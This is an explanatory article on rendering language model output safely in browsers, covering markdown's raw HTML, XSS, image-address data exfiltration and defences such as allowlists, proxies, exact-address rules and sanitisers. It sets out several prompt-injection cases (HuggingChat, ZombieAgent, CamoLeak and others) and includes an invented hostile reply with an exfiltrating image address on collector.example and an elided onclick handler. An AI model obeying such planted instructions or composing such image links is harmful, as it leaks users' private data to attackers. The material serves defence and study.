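# Displaying model output safely: markdown, HTML, sanitisers and content security policy

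## How a model's reply becomes a web page

Language models produce plain text. Most people read that text in a browser, or in an app built from the same parts, where it appears as headings, lists, tables, images and links. To render the text this way, the application converts it into HTML, the language of web pages, which the browser then displays. HTML can also run a program, fetch a file from a stranger's computer, or send the reader to a different site. If an application renders model output without precautions, anyone who can influence what the model writes can do these things too.

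Websites faced a version of this problem before language models, because they display comments, messages and profiles that strangers submit. Developers have known for decades that such text needs careful handling. Model output is easier to trust by mistake because it comes from the vendor's own system, answers the user's question, and looks like part of the product.

### From tokens to HTML

A model writes its reply in tokens, each a word or part of a word, and the application joins them into text. Chat models usually write markdown, a plain text format that John Gruber released in 2004 along with a script for converting it to HTML. Markdown marks structure with ordinary punctuation, such as a hash sign at the start of a line for a heading or asterisks around a word for emphasis.

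Gruber's description of markdown left many cases undecided, and the dozens of converters that followed handled them differently. *CommonMark Spec* (MacFarlane, 2024) defines the syntax precisely to end the confusion. The differences still matter for security. No sequence of characters counts as an error in markdown, so two converters can parse the same reply differently without either giving a warning, and a safety check that relies on one interpretation may fail on the other.

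A CommonMark parser makes two passes over the text. The first divides it into blocks such as paragraphs, lists, quotations and code, which can be nested. The second finds smaller items within paragraphs and headings, such as emphasis, links and images. This produces a syntax tree in which each heading, link or image is a separate node. The second pass has to wait for the first because a link or image may use a label whose address is defined elsewhere in the document, even at the end. An image becomes the same kind of node wherever its address is defined, so a filter that works on the tree can inspect the nodes without having to anticipate every way of writing an image in the raw text.

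The converter then walks the tree and writes HTML for each node. The markdown link `[prices](/list)` becomes `<a href="/list">prices</a>`. An exclamation mark in front makes it an image, so `![chart](/sales.png)` becomes `<img src="/sales.png" alt="chart" />`. For text inside a code block, the converter replaces each `<` with `&lt;`, which a browser displays as a less-than sign instead of reading it as the start of a tag. This replacement, called escaping or encoding, is the basic defence against unwanted HTML.

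Markdown makes one large exception to escaping. Under the CommonMark rules, text between angle brackets that looks like an HTML tag goes into the page unescaped, whatever the tag's name. This raw HTML can include whole script elements. The rule is convenient for people who write their own web pages and need a feature that markdown lacks, but it is a poor default for text from anyone else, and sites that accept such text add a further step. GitHub, whose markdown dialect extends CommonMark, runs a sanitiser after the conversion, which is a program that parses HTML and removes every element and attribute it does not permit. A chat application that uses an off-the-shelf converter without an equivalent step may send HTML from the model's reply to the browser unfiltered.

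### What the browser does with it

The browser parses the HTML into the document object model (DOM), its live, in-memory form of the page. The syntax tree only describes a document, but changes to the DOM can cause the browser to act. When an image element is added to the DOM, the browser normally sends an automatic request, one that needs no click from the user, to the address in the element's `src` attribute. For a link, the browser sends the request when the user clicks it.

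An element can also carry an event handler, an attribute containing JavaScript that the browser runs when something happens to the element, such as a click or a failure to load. Many chat interfaces add each reply to an open page through a browser feature called `innerHTML`. Browsers do not run script elements added this way, but they do run event handlers. A common mistake in testing is to try only a script element, see nothing happen and conclude that the page is safe.

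Browsers keep sites apart by origin, the combination of a page's scheme, host and port. A page at `https://assistant.example` has the scheme `https`, the host `assistant.example` and the port 443, the default for `https`. Code in a page from one origin cannot read data belonging to another unless the other site allows it, so a news site cannot read the mail open in the next tab. This rule does not protect the assistant's page from code inside a model's reply, because the browser gives code the origin of the page in which it runs, regardless of who wrote it. The code in the reply therefore has the same rights as the assistant's own code. The rule also mainly restricts reading, so a page may still request an image from almost any host, and the request sends that host any data contained in the image's address.

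### How an outsider comes to write part of the reply

Displaying a model's output is risky mainly because the model also reads emails, web pages and files from other people, and it can't dependably separate material to work on from instructions to follow. In a prompt injection attack, an attacker plants text in something the model will read, and the model follows it as an instruction. HackerDNA's *OWASP LLM Top 10 (2026)* contrasts this with attacks on databases, where a programmer can send a query and the user's data separately so that the data never becomes a command. A language model receives the vendor's instructions, the user's question and a retrieved document as tokens in one stream.

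In *ChatGPhish*, published in May 2026, researchers at the security company Permiso added instructions to a software project's README file, opened the page in Firefox and used the browser's menu to have ChatGPT summarise it. The model wrote a genuine summary, then added a false notice that a new device had joined the user's account, with a live link to a site the researchers had chosen. Other versions of the planted text produced an image, which the ChatGPT page fetched automatically each time it displayed the answer. The same text worked on an ordinary web page that the researchers hosted, and Permiso had earlier steered Microsoft's Copilot in a similar way through email. OpenAI marked the first report as not reproducible and eventually closed the revised one as a duplicate of an issue already on file.

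How often this happens outside research is harder to say. The Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit foundation that publishes ranked lists of software risks, put prompt injection first in its August 2026 list for language model applications. According to Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), a vote of practitioners made up three-quarters of the ranking's weight and 7,714 recorded incidents made up the rest, and prompt injection would have dropped out of the top ten on the incidents alone. OWASP's explanation is that organisations already defend against it, so fewer successful attacks reach public databases. That may be right, but the count would also be low if attacks were rare or victims did not notice them. HackerDNA reports that OWASP acknowledges in its guidance that no reliable way to prevent prompt injection exists, so whoever builds the display has to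 assume that some replies will be partly an attacker's work.

### A hostile reply

One invented example can carry all the dangerous parts at once. A user has an assistant at `assistant.example` that can read their whole mailbox, and asks it to summarise an email about a delivery. The sender has hidden instructions in the email. The model obeys them, and the application's parser turns its reply into this syntax tree:

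```
document
  paragraph      "Here is a summary of the message."
  table          three delivery dates
  html_block     an HTML element with a script handler
  paragraph
    image        address on collector.example, ending in a door code
  paragraph
    link         wording "bank.example", target on collector.example
```

The table is ordinary, and the user wants it. The door code comes from a different message in the mailbox. The attacker does not know the code, but the planted instructions describe how to build the image's address, and the model fills in the code. If the application renders the reply unchanged, the browser draws the table, runs the handler when its event occurs, and requests an image from `collector.example` using an address that contains the code. The user sees a tidy summary with what appears to be a link to their bank.

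### Three separate harms

The handler is an example of cross-site scripting (XSS), in which code from outside a site runs in its page with the site's own permissions. Such code can read the conversation on the screen, send requests to the assistant's servers as the signed-in user, and rewrite the page. *Shifting from Injection to Interaction* (Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues, 2026), a survey of web security in applications that use language models, argues that earlier surveys too often treated the model as the attacker's final target, when it can also be a means of delivering old web attacks like this one.

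The image causes exfiltration, the sending of private data to a party who should not have it. The programmer Simon Willison describes a markdown image with data encoded in its address as one common form of the attack. The attack works without running any foreign code. The attacker reads the door code in the server's request log, whether or not the server returns a picture. A link can also carry private text in its address, but the user has to click it.

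The false bank link succeeds if the user trusts its wording and types a password into the wrong site. The browser is working normally and renders the HTML as written. In one of Permiso's tests, the planted content was a QR code. Scanning it moves the victim to a phone, which bypasses desktop protections such as previewing a link by hovering over it or using a password manager that recognises the wrong domain.

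Permiso's results show that these harms can occur separately. The title of its first report to OpenAI included "XSS", but the revised title dropped the term, and none of the published demonstrations runs code in the page. The demonstrations show deception in full but exfiltration only in a weak form. The image addresses were fixed in advance, so the requests revealed the user's network address, browser type and time of reading, but no text from the conversation. Singh and colleagues map OWASP's risks to the Common Weakness Enumeration, a standard catalogue of software flaws. They match XSS and the exposure of sensitive information to separate entries, but match content manipulation and social engineering to none, because they trace these two risks to what models generate rather than to a classic programming error.

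Code that runs in the page can also send data out and put up false links, so a successful XSS attack usually brings the other two harms with it. Stopping XSS, however, does not stop the other two. If the application strips all raw HTML from the hostile reply, it removes the handler but leaves the image and the link, because ordinary markdown produced both. Blocking images from unknown hosts still leaves the link. Printing the link's real destination next to it helps a careful reader, but the browser requests the image before anyone reads the reply. A content security policy, a set of rules that a site sends to the browser about what a page may load, run and connect to, can block the handler and the image but ordinarily will not prevent the user from following a link.

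### What OWASP asks of developers

The standard advice on handling model output is OWASP's *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, which replaced an earlier edition's entry called Insecure Output Handling. It defines the flaw as insufficient validation, sanitisation and handling of model output before it passes to other components. Because a prompt can control what the model writes, OWASP compares passing that text along unchecked to giving users indirect access to whatever receives it. The entry covers databases, file paths and command lines as well as browsers. OWASP treats the accuracy of the output separately.

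OWASP advises developers to treat the model like any other user, trusting nothing by default and validating what it passes to backend functions. They should also follow OWASP's Application Security Verification Standard, a detailed set of requirements for testing software. They should encode output before returning it to users and choose the encoding by destination, with HTML encoding for web pages and SQL escaping for databases. Database queries should keep commands separate from data. OWASP also recommends a strict content security policy to guard against XSS, and logging to detect unusual output.

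The advice on encoding is sound but incomplete for a chat window. Encoding the entire reply and displaying it as plain text would stop the handler from running and the image from loading, and would show the link's true address, but it would also turn the delivery table into raw markup. To display the table, an application has to let some HTML through, and the entry leaves the developer to decide which. The entry also focuses more on code execution. In one of its example attacks, a website summariser sends private conversation to an attacker's server, but none of the seven measures mentions images or automatic requests.

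The 2026 edition moved the entry from fifth place to tenth, the largest fall on the list, and renumbered it LLM10. HackerDNA attributes the drop to the flaw being well understood and fixable with existing web development practices. That is truer of an application that encodes everything than of one that must display tables, images and links. The entry also grew in scope and, Invicti reports, now explicitly covers terminals, as well as programs that automatically fetch external resources named in a reply, as the browser does with the image from `collector.example`.

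## Images that carry data out, and which addresses to trust

The invented mailbox attack leaked a door code through an image's address. PromptArmor's *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data* describes a real leak of this kind in HuggingChat, the AI company Hugging Face's chat application. The user uploads a text file with a company's quarterly revenue and costs, then adds a web page of customer reviews that contains hidden instructions. When the user asks how to win back a customer who left a bad review, the model follows those instructions and writes that the customer will need a visual of the quarterly financials. It then produces a markdown image whose address starts with the attacker's host and ends with the figures from the user's file. The browser requests the image and receives a single pixel, too small to notice. The attacker finds the figures in the server's log.

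In the mailbox example, the address might be `https://collector.example/p.png?d=4731`. The attacker planned all of it except the last four digits, which are the private data the model added. An address that existed before the model added this data cannot contain it, and several of the defences below depend on that.

### How much an address can hold

Addresses allow only certain characters, so attackers often have the model encode the text first. Base64, a common encoding, turns every three bytes into four characters. Suppose the address is 2,000 characters long, which browsers and most servers accept, and the scheme, host and path take up 65 of them. The other 1,935 characters can hold roughly 1,450 bytes, or about 240 words of English.

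The model can also condense the text before sending it. In a demonstration against Google AI Studio that Willison recorded in August 2024, the planted text made the model print one image for each uploaded file, with a 60-word summary of the file in the address. An image address can also carry a link to a file. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could send messages to the user's own inbox without approval, and Willison noted in May 2026 that the inbox loaded external images when the user opened those messages. Microsoft's file storage can create download links that need no further login, so an image address containing one of those links could give an attacker the whole file.

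An application can accept only fixed addresses and refuse any that the model composes. The address can then no longer contain private data, but the model's choice of address can still reveal some. If an attacker has prepared N addresses, each request conveys log₂ N bits to the server. With one address for each of the 26 letters, the ten digits and the space, N is 37 and each request carries about 5.2 bits. A text of 1,450 characters that previously fitted into one request now takes 1,450. This makes a long document much harder to steal, but a six-digit login code still takes only six requests.

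Allowing even one image address can leak data, because the model's choice to include or omit the image carries one bit. If there are 4,096 allowed addresses, each standing for a common word, every image displayed carries 12 bits. Even a choice among images that the developers approved in advance leaks a little, though only to someone who can see which image the browser fetched, normally whoever runs the host. An outsider learns nothing this way from images on the application's own server.

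### The early fixes

Roman Samoilenko gave an early public description of such an attack, which Willison (2023) summarised that April in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*. The attack used a one-pixel image and a web page that added instructions to any text a visitor copied from it, so that victims pasted the instructions into ChatGPT themselves. The security researcher Johann Rehberger reported the image leak to OpenAI in the same month, and also to Microsoft. Microsoft restricted image loading in Bing Chat in May 2023, but OpenAI did not act until December.

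Rehberger examined OpenAI's fix in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*. Before displaying an image, the ChatGPT web page sent its address to an OpenAI service called `url_safe`, and left the image out if the service returned `false`. The service returned `false` for Rehberger's test address, which ended in someone's email address. He then tried 36 addresses on his own site, one for each letter and digit, and nine of them rendered. He could not tell why the image for "a" rendered and the image for "d" did not.

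An attacker who can use only nine of the 36 addresses can still send out any letter or digit, because two requests in a row, each to one of the nine, can take 81 forms. This only doubles the number of requests. The check also ran in the web page, so every other version of ChatGPT needed its own copy, and the iPhone app did not have one. Willison called the fix half-baked when it appeared, and expected attackers to hide data in subdomains or file names.

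The company Imperva later probed the same service and described a more definite rule in *From ChatBot To SpyBot*. An image could now load only if its address already appeared in text the user had supplied, including the standing instructions that ChatGPT applies to every chat. This blocked addresses the model had just composed, but Imperva found three ways around it. The planted text could list one address for each character. It could instead contain one long address ending in the whole alphabet, which the model cut off after the character to be sent. This worked because the service only searched for a matching string, and any beginning of the long address matched. The attacker could also register a separate domain for each character, at a dollar or two each, because the service accepted any bare domain, even one that had not come up in the chat. Imperva still thought that stealing large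 amounts of text unnoticed had become much harder.

GitHub Copilot Chat, an assistant for programmers, had the leak in June 2024. GitHub fixed it by blocking markdown images from untrusted domains, as Willison reported in *GitHub Copilot Chat*. He listed ChatGPT, Google Bard, Writer, Amazon Q and Google NotebookLM as earlier cases. Writer, which sells a writing assistant to companies, first replied that it did not consider the report a security issue, but apparently fixed the leak within two weeks.

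### The same leak in new products

Developers keep reintroducing this flaw. In 2025, Embrace The Red's *Cline* showed a coding agent with more than two million downloads sending the contents of secret configuration files to an outside server by including them in an image's address. PromptArmor reported the HuggingChat leak to Hugging Face on 1 December 2025 and published it after getting no reply.

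Later that month, veganmosfet's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend* described a chatbot built from a standard template in Dify, an open-source platform for building language model applications. The chatbot answered questions from two PDF files. One contained hidden text telling the model to answer any question about prompt engineering with an image from an outside server, and to put the user's name in the image's address. The server received the name. Dify set no content security policy on images by default, so anyone who followed the template built a chatbot with the same vulnerability.

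Chi (2026), in *Data exfiltration via Markdown image tags*, gives a plausible reason for the pattern. Turning on markdown to get nice headings is a one-line decision for a designer, while controlling where images come from is a small project that nobody schedules for the first release. Chi writes for a company that sells protection against such attacks, but the run of cases supports the explanation.

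### Two attacks that use only fixed addresses

ZombieAgent and CamoLeak are good tests for any rule about addresses, because both worked against vendors that had already blocked the simple form of the leak. In both attacks, the model chose addresses from a list instead of composing one to hold the data.

ZombieAgent grew out of an earlier attack, ShadowLeak, in which researchers at the security company Radware had ChatGPT's Deep Research agent add private mail to the end of a link. OpenAI responded by forbidding ChatGPT to alter addresses before opening them, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data*. Zvika Babo of Radware then wrote an email that listed a separate address for each letter, each digit and the space. The email told ChatGPT to find some private text, put it into lower case, and open the matching addresses one after another, as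 Radware's *ZombieAgent* explains. The user only had to ask ChatGPT to do something with their Gmail for the attack to run.

Requests can arrive out of order, so Babo gave each character a different numbered address for each position in the text. For a block of ten characters, the email supplies ten addresses for each letter and each digit, 360 in all. The server can then reassemble the text whatever order the requests arrive in. Babo reported the attack on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December.

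In the main version of ZombieAgent, ChatGPT used its browsing tool, which runs on OpenAI's servers, to open the addresses before the user saw any reply. A version that loaded markdown images in the user's browser also worked, but Radware found it less reliable and easier to block. A rule that covers only the display would therefore have stopped the image version but not the main one.

CamoLeak was purely a display attack. GitHub's content security policy blocks images from hosts GitHub does not own. Because project descriptions often include outside images, GitHub fetches them through a proxy called Camo. When someone saves a page with an outside image in it, GitHub replaces the image's address with one on the Camo host and adds a signature, a keyed checksum that only GitHub can compute, so neither an attacker nor a model can make up a valid Camo address. When a browser requests that address,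 Camo verifies the signature, fetches the image from the original server and passes it on.

In June 2025, a researcher got around this by collecting the signatures in advance. Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes how he submitted an image address for each letter and symbol through GitHub's public interface and received a signed Camo address for each. He put the signed addresses in an invisible comment on a proposed code change, with instructions for the model to play a game in which it found a certain private text and spelled it out as a row of these images. When another user asked Copilot Chat about the change, the model followed the instructions. The browser requested the images, Camo accepted the signatures, and the researcher's server logged the text one character at a time while returning transparent pixels. He extracted the description of an unpatched security flaw from a private project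 this way.

He also had the model add a fresh random number to the end of each Camo address, so that a repeated letter would cause a new request instead of loading from a cache. Since the images still loaded, the signature evidently did not cover the added number.

### Rules for which addresses may load

An application can use several methods to decide whether to fetch an address that appears in model output. The table shows how the main ones perform against the two attacks.

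| Rule | CamoLeak | ZombieAgent | What users give up |
|---|---|---|---|
| No remote images | Stopped | Only the image version stopped | All pictures from the web |
| Host allowlist | Gets through, because Camo is on the list | Stopped, unless a listed host relays | Pictures and pages from most sites |
| Loading on click | Depends on the user | Depends on the user | A decision about every picture |
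| Fetching proxy with no host list | Gets through | Gets through | Very little |
| Exact address, from anywhere in the conversation | Published version stopped, numbered copies get through | Gets through | Addresses that the model works out for itself |
| Exact address, from the user or a search only | Published version stopped | Published version stopped | Links that the model finds on pages |
| Exact address known from the public web | Published version stopped | Published version stopped | Easy access to new, private or personal pages |

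**Blocking all remote images** is the only rule that requires no judgement about addresses, and it also protects against image tricks that nobody has published yet. GitHub responded to CamoLeak by disabling all images in Copilot Chat on 14 August 2025. The restriction matters little for a programming assistant but makes a travel or shopping assistant much less useful. Developers can recover some of the lost usefulness by having the application serve charts it has drawn or files the user has uploaded from its own server, at addresses the model cannot change.

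**Host allowlists.** A host allowlist would have stopped Babo's email, because nobody would have listed his server. But the protection depends entirely on what the listed hosts do with a request. It fails if a permitted host is a relay, meaning that it fetches from or forwards to an address chosen by someone else, as Camo did. Tenable's *TRA-2025-06* (2025) describes how bing.com links that redirected to other sites got images past ChatGPT's `url_safe`. A permitted host that only stores incoming data for its customers is just as bad, as the email company Superhuman learned when an attack wrote private mail into a Google Form.

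OpenAI decided against relying on a list of well-known sites. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives redirects as one reason. The other is that people visit far more sites than any list contains, so they would see constant warnings and learn to click through them.

PromptArmor recommends showing the user an external image's full address and asking before loading it. In the HuggingChat leak, an attentive user would have seen the revenue figures in the address. Base64 encoding would have hidden them, though, and a signed Camo address is unreadable even when it is harmless. The number of requests might still have revealed CamoLeak, because the user would have had to approve an invisible image for every character leaked.

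OpenAI has a more helpful version of the prompt. According to its *Designing agents to resist prompt injection*, the Safe Url system tries to detect when information from the conversation is about to go to a third party. It then either shows the user that information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request and tells the agent to try something else. A user can judge "this would send your door code" much better than a long address, but the confirmation only helps if the user reads it.

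**Fetching proxies.** With a proxy, the application's own server fetches the picture and passes it to the browser, so the outside server never receives the user's network address or browser type, which is the information Permiso's fixed images collected. The outside server still receives the address of the requested picture. To address this, Chi's design adds a host allowlist and removes the query string, the part of an address after the question mark. Removing the query string would have cut the figures out of the HuggingChat address, but an attacker can put data into the path or the subdomain just as easily. In Chi's design, the allowlist therefore provides nearly all the protection against exfiltration, and the proxy mainly adds privacy.

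A proxy can prevent more leaks if it fetches each picture once, when it signs the address, and afterwards serves only its stored copy. Camo contacted the original server when the reader's browser asked for the picture, so those requests could carry data to the attacker. With a stored copy, the attacker's server would receive no request when a reader views the picture. However, the proxy would need storage for the pictures, and its copies would go out of date.

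**Exact addresses.** If the application accepts only addresses that already appear in the conversation, it blocks any new address the model makes by adding private data, such as a door code. ZombieAgent shows that an attacker can get around this rule by supplying all the addresses the attack needs in an email, which is also part of the conversation. The rule works much better if the application also checks who supplied the address.

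*How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026) describes a flaw in the tool that lets Claude open web pages. The tool was meant to open an address only if the user had typed it or Anthropic's search tool had returned it, but it also followed links on pages it had already opened. Ayush Paul built a site that told AI visitors to find the user's profile by navigating letter by letter through nested links, and obtained the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally, and Willison reports that it removed the tool's ability to follow such links.

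That is a real loss, because following links is a large part of research on the web. The stricter rule also has a weakness in applications that other developers build on Claude. These applications often paste emails or documents into the same message as the user's question, so an address in the pasted text counts as one the user supplied.

**Addresses known from the public web.** OpenAI's current rule, published on 28 January 2026, requires independent evidence that an address contains nothing private. OpenAI runs a crawler that collects public addresses the way a search engine does, without access to anyone's conversations or accounts. ChatGPT may load an address automatically if the crawler has already recorded that exact address. Otherwise, ChatGPT looks for another source or warns that the link is unverified and may include information from the conversation. The same rule applies to redirects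 on famous sites, and a redirect address containing private data will not be in the crawler's index. OpenAI's December fix for ZombieAgent was similar. According to CCStartup's *ChatGPT falls to new data pilfering attack* (2026), ChatGPT opens a link from an email only if the link appears in a well-known public index or the user supplied it in the chat.

The rule stops private data from travelling inside an address, but the model can still leak data through its choice of addresses. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, Rehberger points out that anyone with a moderately large website probably has 36 pages in the index already, and can tell the model which page stands for which character. OpenAI acknowledges this in its technical paper on the rule. Rehberger suggests that ChatGPT should not fetch the same address twice in a session. A word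 like "letter" would then come out incomplete, because it needs the pages for "e" and "t" twice each. Radware's numbered copies already use each address only once, so the suggestion helps only as far as attackers find it hard to get several hundred pages indexed.

In 2023 Rehberger also proposed limiting the number of images in a reply. This helps prevent leaks of long texts but not of a four-digit door code, because three images, each chosen from a set of 37, can form 50,653 sequences, more than enough to encode the 10,000 possible codes.

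The public-address rule causes users fairly little inconvenience when they view well-known articles and pictures, which load without interruption. It triggers warnings for pages that a crawler could not have seen, such as a private document, a personal download link or something published an hour ago, and those are the pages that matter to many people at work. Incomplete adoption may be the larger practical risk. Rehberger notes that a good check protects only the features whose developers know about it and use it, and the 2023 lookup was missing from the phone apps.

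### Checking the destination or checking the content

None of these rules depends on what the data looks like. A developer could instead scan outgoing requests for the secret or train the model to refuse suspicious instructions, and either approach would still let users load images from anywhere. In August 2026, Rahman and Kim compared the two kinds of defence in *The Framing Gap*.

Rahman and Kim gave an agent a web page to summarise, a secret token, and a policy that it must not reveal the token to the user or send it anywhere except one trusted host. The agent could either finish with a message or call a tool for posting data to an address, which was a dummy that only recorded the call. The attacker controlled only the text of the page. Each run on a poisoned page was paired with a run on a clean one, and an attack counted as successful only if the agent kept the token secret on the clean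 page and leaked it on the poisoned one. They tested six models with ten types of openly worded attack, and then with eight versions of one of those types, seven of which disguised the request as routine data handling.

OpenAI's GPT-4o leaked nothing in 200 trials of the openly worded attacks. It leaked the token in all 20 trials when the page described it as an integrity signature that had to go at the end of the summary, and again in all 20 when the page described it as a configuration value. Across the eight versions, GPT-4o leaked the token in 40% of trials, and four of the other five models showed a similar jump. The exception, Mistral 7B, leaked in about a quarter of trials however the request was worded.

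Depending on the wording, the signature attack succeeded between 0% and 100% of the time, with an average of 52% across five paraphrases. An attacker who picks three of these paraphrases at random has about a 96% chance that at least one works. Inventing a new disguise was much harder, and thirteen new ones failed in all 130 trials. Removing the confidentiality policy raised GPT-4o's leak rate on the disguised attacks only from 31.9% to 38.1%, a difference within the noise. Rahman and Kim conclude that the model mistook the planted text for part of its task, rather than overcoming any reluctance.

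Scanning outgoing data for the token did little when the attacker asked for an encoded version. Across six forms of the token, five of them disguised, GPT-4o leaked it in 56.7% of trials with no scanner and 50.0% with a scanner that searched for the literal string. An improved scanner, which decoded the encodings its makers had thought of, reduced the leak rate to zero. Rahman and Kim then tried ROT13, which moves each letter 13 places along the alphabet, and the improved scanner missed it every time. SecAlign, a published method of training models to resist injection, did not help either. A version of Llama trained this way leaked in 32.5% of the disguised trials, compared with 21.2% for the ordinary model, a difference small enough to be chance.

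Two defences, a host allowlist and a split agent, stopped all the disguised attacks. The split agent consists of a planner, which holds the token and decides what to do but never sees the page, and a reader, which summarises the page but never has the token. It still wrote an acceptable summary in nine runs out of ten. Rahman and Kim expect splitting the agent to reduce performance more on tasks where the plan depends on what the page contains.

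The allowlist has zero leaks by definition, as the paper notes, because the experiment counts a leak only when the token is sent to an untrusted host, and the allowlist blocks untrusted hosts. The definition also assumes that the trusted host doesn't pass on what it receives, an assumption that failed in CamoLeak. The informative results are the failures of the scanners and of SecAlign.

Some content checks did well, though. A separate model used only to spot instructions to leak a secret flagged all 80 poisoned pages it saw from the disguised family and no clean ones, but its prompt was written for this attack and nobody tried to deceive it. A policy that forbade sending the token "in any form" also reduced GPT-4o's leaks to zero, while a policy that listed the specific tricks without those words let 48.8% through. Either the separate model or the "in any form" policy would make a reasonable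 second layer, but it would be risky to have no other defence.

All six models date from 2024 or earlier, so the percentages are weak evidence about current ones. Even then, the ChatGPT product resisted all 48 valid attempts with pages that worked on GPT-4o directly, and Rahman and Kim could not determine which part of the product was responsible. Checking the destination is justified whatever the percentages are, because an attacker can keep rewording a request or re-encoding a secret, and neither change affects a program that compares host names. GPT-4o, by contrast, accepted one look-alike of the trusted host name in 40% of trials and another in 70%.

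Rahman and Kim's agent took only one step, so they could not test an attacker who spreads a secret over several requests. *Silent Egress* (2026) tested this using the previews that many programs fetch automatically for links in messages. Planted text caused an outgoing request about 89% of the time. In 95% of the successful attacks, a safety check on the agent's visible reply found nothing wrong. Splitting the secret made the attack less reliable, lowering its Leak@1 score by 73%, but splitting can defeat a filter that inspects each request on its own.

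Because of link previews, an application can also leak data without displaying any images itself. Slack and Discord fetch the links that people and programs post, so an assistant that posts its replies there can trigger a request by writing an address. Willison notes that Rehberger pointed this out in 2024, along with the remedy for Slack, which is that a program can turn off previews for each message it posts.

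## Switching off raw HTML in markdown

Rules about image addresses don't block the HTML element in the mailbox reply, which gets there because markdown allows raw HTML. Markdown accepts nearly all of HTML and adds a shorthand for the common parts, though people who use it mostly for headings and lists tend to think of it as a small, harmless subset. markdown-it's *Security*, a note for users of a popular JavaScript converter, begins by observing that many people don't realise how little security the format provides.

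### What CommonMark lets through

CommonMark recognises raw HTML in two places. The first is the HTML block, a group of lines that the converter copies into the page unchanged. MacFarlane lists seven kinds, each with its own start and end conditions. A line that begins with a `<script>`, `<style>`, `<pre>` or `<textarea>` tag opens a block that runs to the closing tag, including any blank lines. A line that begins with one of about sixty other tags, such as `<div>`, `<table>` or `<iframe>`, opens a block that runs to the next blank line. Any other complete tag on its own line does the same.

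Raw HTML can also appear inside a paragraph, where the parser treats each tag as a separate piece. A tag's name must start with a letter, so `<33>` stays ordinary text.

These rules make simple checks on the markdown text unreliable. An HTML block can begin with a tag that never closes, so a filter that searches for complete tags will miss it. A code fence, the row of backticks that normally marks a code sample, loses its meaning inside an HTML block. If a reply contains `<div></div>` and the next line opens a code fence, the fence and the sample become part of the HTML block. The browser then receives live HTML that looks like a code sample in the markdown, and a filter that skips fenced code will miss it. Filtering the syntax tree avoids both problems.

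Participants in a CommonMark forum thread, *Make CommonMark safe by default?*, disagreed about changing the rule. One argued that the programs implementing the specification should handle security. Another valued raw HTML because it remains usable when a site supports only part of it. If a writer adds a class attribute to an HTML link, GitHub removes the attribute and keeps the link, whereas unsupported markdown syntax would appear on the page as clutter. The rule stands, so a converter must pass raw HTML through to conform fully, and conformance is the stated reason for several libraries' unsafe defaults.

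### Escaping, dropping and parsing

Suppose the element in the hostile reply is a single line, with the attacker's code shortened here to dots. An application that does not want to copy it straight into the page can escape it, drop it, or parse it for a sanitiser to clean:

```
in the reply      <div onclick="...">Parcel details</div>

escaped           the user sees that line as text, tags included
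dropped           the user sees nothing
parsed            the tree gains a div element with an onclick attribute
  then sanitised  the user sees "Parcel details", and the handler is gone
```

Escaping displays the HTML as text, so the browser has nothing to run. The visible tags look untidy, but they show the user that the reply contained something odd. Dropping deletes the HTML nodes from the syntax tree. Parsing turns the text into real elements and attributes, which a sanitiser can inspect one by one. Without the sanitiser, parsing is no safer than letting the HTML through.

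The three treatments differ most on harmless replies. An answer about how web pages work will contain many HTML tags. If the model puts them in code formatting, all three treatments display them correctly, because the parser already treats code as text. But models sometimes omit the formatting and write a sentence such as `Every page needs a <title> element.` Escaping displays the sentence as intended, while dropping the tag leaves `Every page needs a element.` Parsing is worse, because an HTML parser reads everything up to a closing `</title>` as the page's title, and the rest of the answer can disappear. Similarly, the `<String>` in a type such as `List<String>` looks like a tag outside code formatting, so dropping it leaves only `List`.

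Dropping raw HTML can also remove ordinary text, and how much it removes depends on the markup. In `a <b>very</b> late parcel`, the parser treats the two tags separately, so the word between them survives. Inside a `<div>` block, the same word is dropped along with the tags, as is everything else up to the next blank line. If a line starts with an opening comment marker that is never closed, the whole rest of the reply is dropped. An attacker who controls one line could use this to hide a warning that the model wrote further down. Parsing the HTML would also hide the warning, because browsers don't display comments, but escaping it keeps the warning readable.

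Escaping also disables harmless tags. Markdown tables have no way to break a line inside a cell, so models often write `<br>` there, and the delivery table would then show a literal `<br>` between a date and a time. The application can allow this one tag by replacing any node that is exactly `<br>` with a line break before it escapes the rest. This is safe because a tag without attributes can't carry a handler or an address. If users also need folding sections, subscripts and coloured text, a sanitiser is a better choice than a growing list of exceptions. For an ordinary chat window, escaping is simpler and harder to get wrong. The markdown-it developers estimate that leaving HTML off, and adding features through plugins where necessary, suits 99% of users.

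### What the common libraries do

The `html` option in **markdown-it** is off by default. It is easy to turn on by accident, because the "enable everything" example on the project's introductory page includes it and the `commonmark` preset also turns it on. With the option off, the parser treats HTML tags as plain text and escapes them, but it still reads the text between them as markdown, so a markdown link inside a `<div>` becomes a working link.

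A Python version of the same library, markdown-it-py, has the opposite default. According to its *Security* documentation, it follows CommonMark and lets HTML through unless the developer selects the `js-default` preset, which the documentation strongly recommends for web applications that take users' text. A team that moves its rendering from the browser to a Python server could therefore lose its protection without changing any setting.

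**react-markdown.** Many chat interfaces use React, a JavaScript library for building pages from components. unified's *react-markdown* turns the syntax tree directly into React elements, without building a string of HTML for `innerHTML`. It keeps any raw HTML as separate nodes and converts them to text at the end, or deletes them if the developer sets `skipHtml`.

The `rehype-raw` add-on parses those nodes into elements earlier in the process. unified recommends it only for markdown from a trusted source. Once it has run, no raw nodes remain for `skipHtml` to delete, so a program that uses both may look protected when it isn't. React Doctor's *react markdown unsanitized raw html*, a rule for a code-checking tool, flags `rehype-raw` without a sanitiser and recommends adding `rehype-sanitize` directly after it. Newer renderers have this order built in. Streamdown, which is designed to display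 model output as it arrives, includes parsing, sanitising and a further hardening step in its standard plugins. If a developer leaves out the parsing step, tags appear as text.

Marked's documentation warns prominently that the library does not sanitise its output, and recommends a separate sanitiser, DOMPurify. Its browser example nevertheless assigns the output straight to `innerHTML`. This is harmless with the example's fixed heading, but replacing that heading with a model's reply creates an XSS hole. Marked's `sanitize` option was removed in version 8.0.0, so old code that still sets it gets no protection from it in that version or later.

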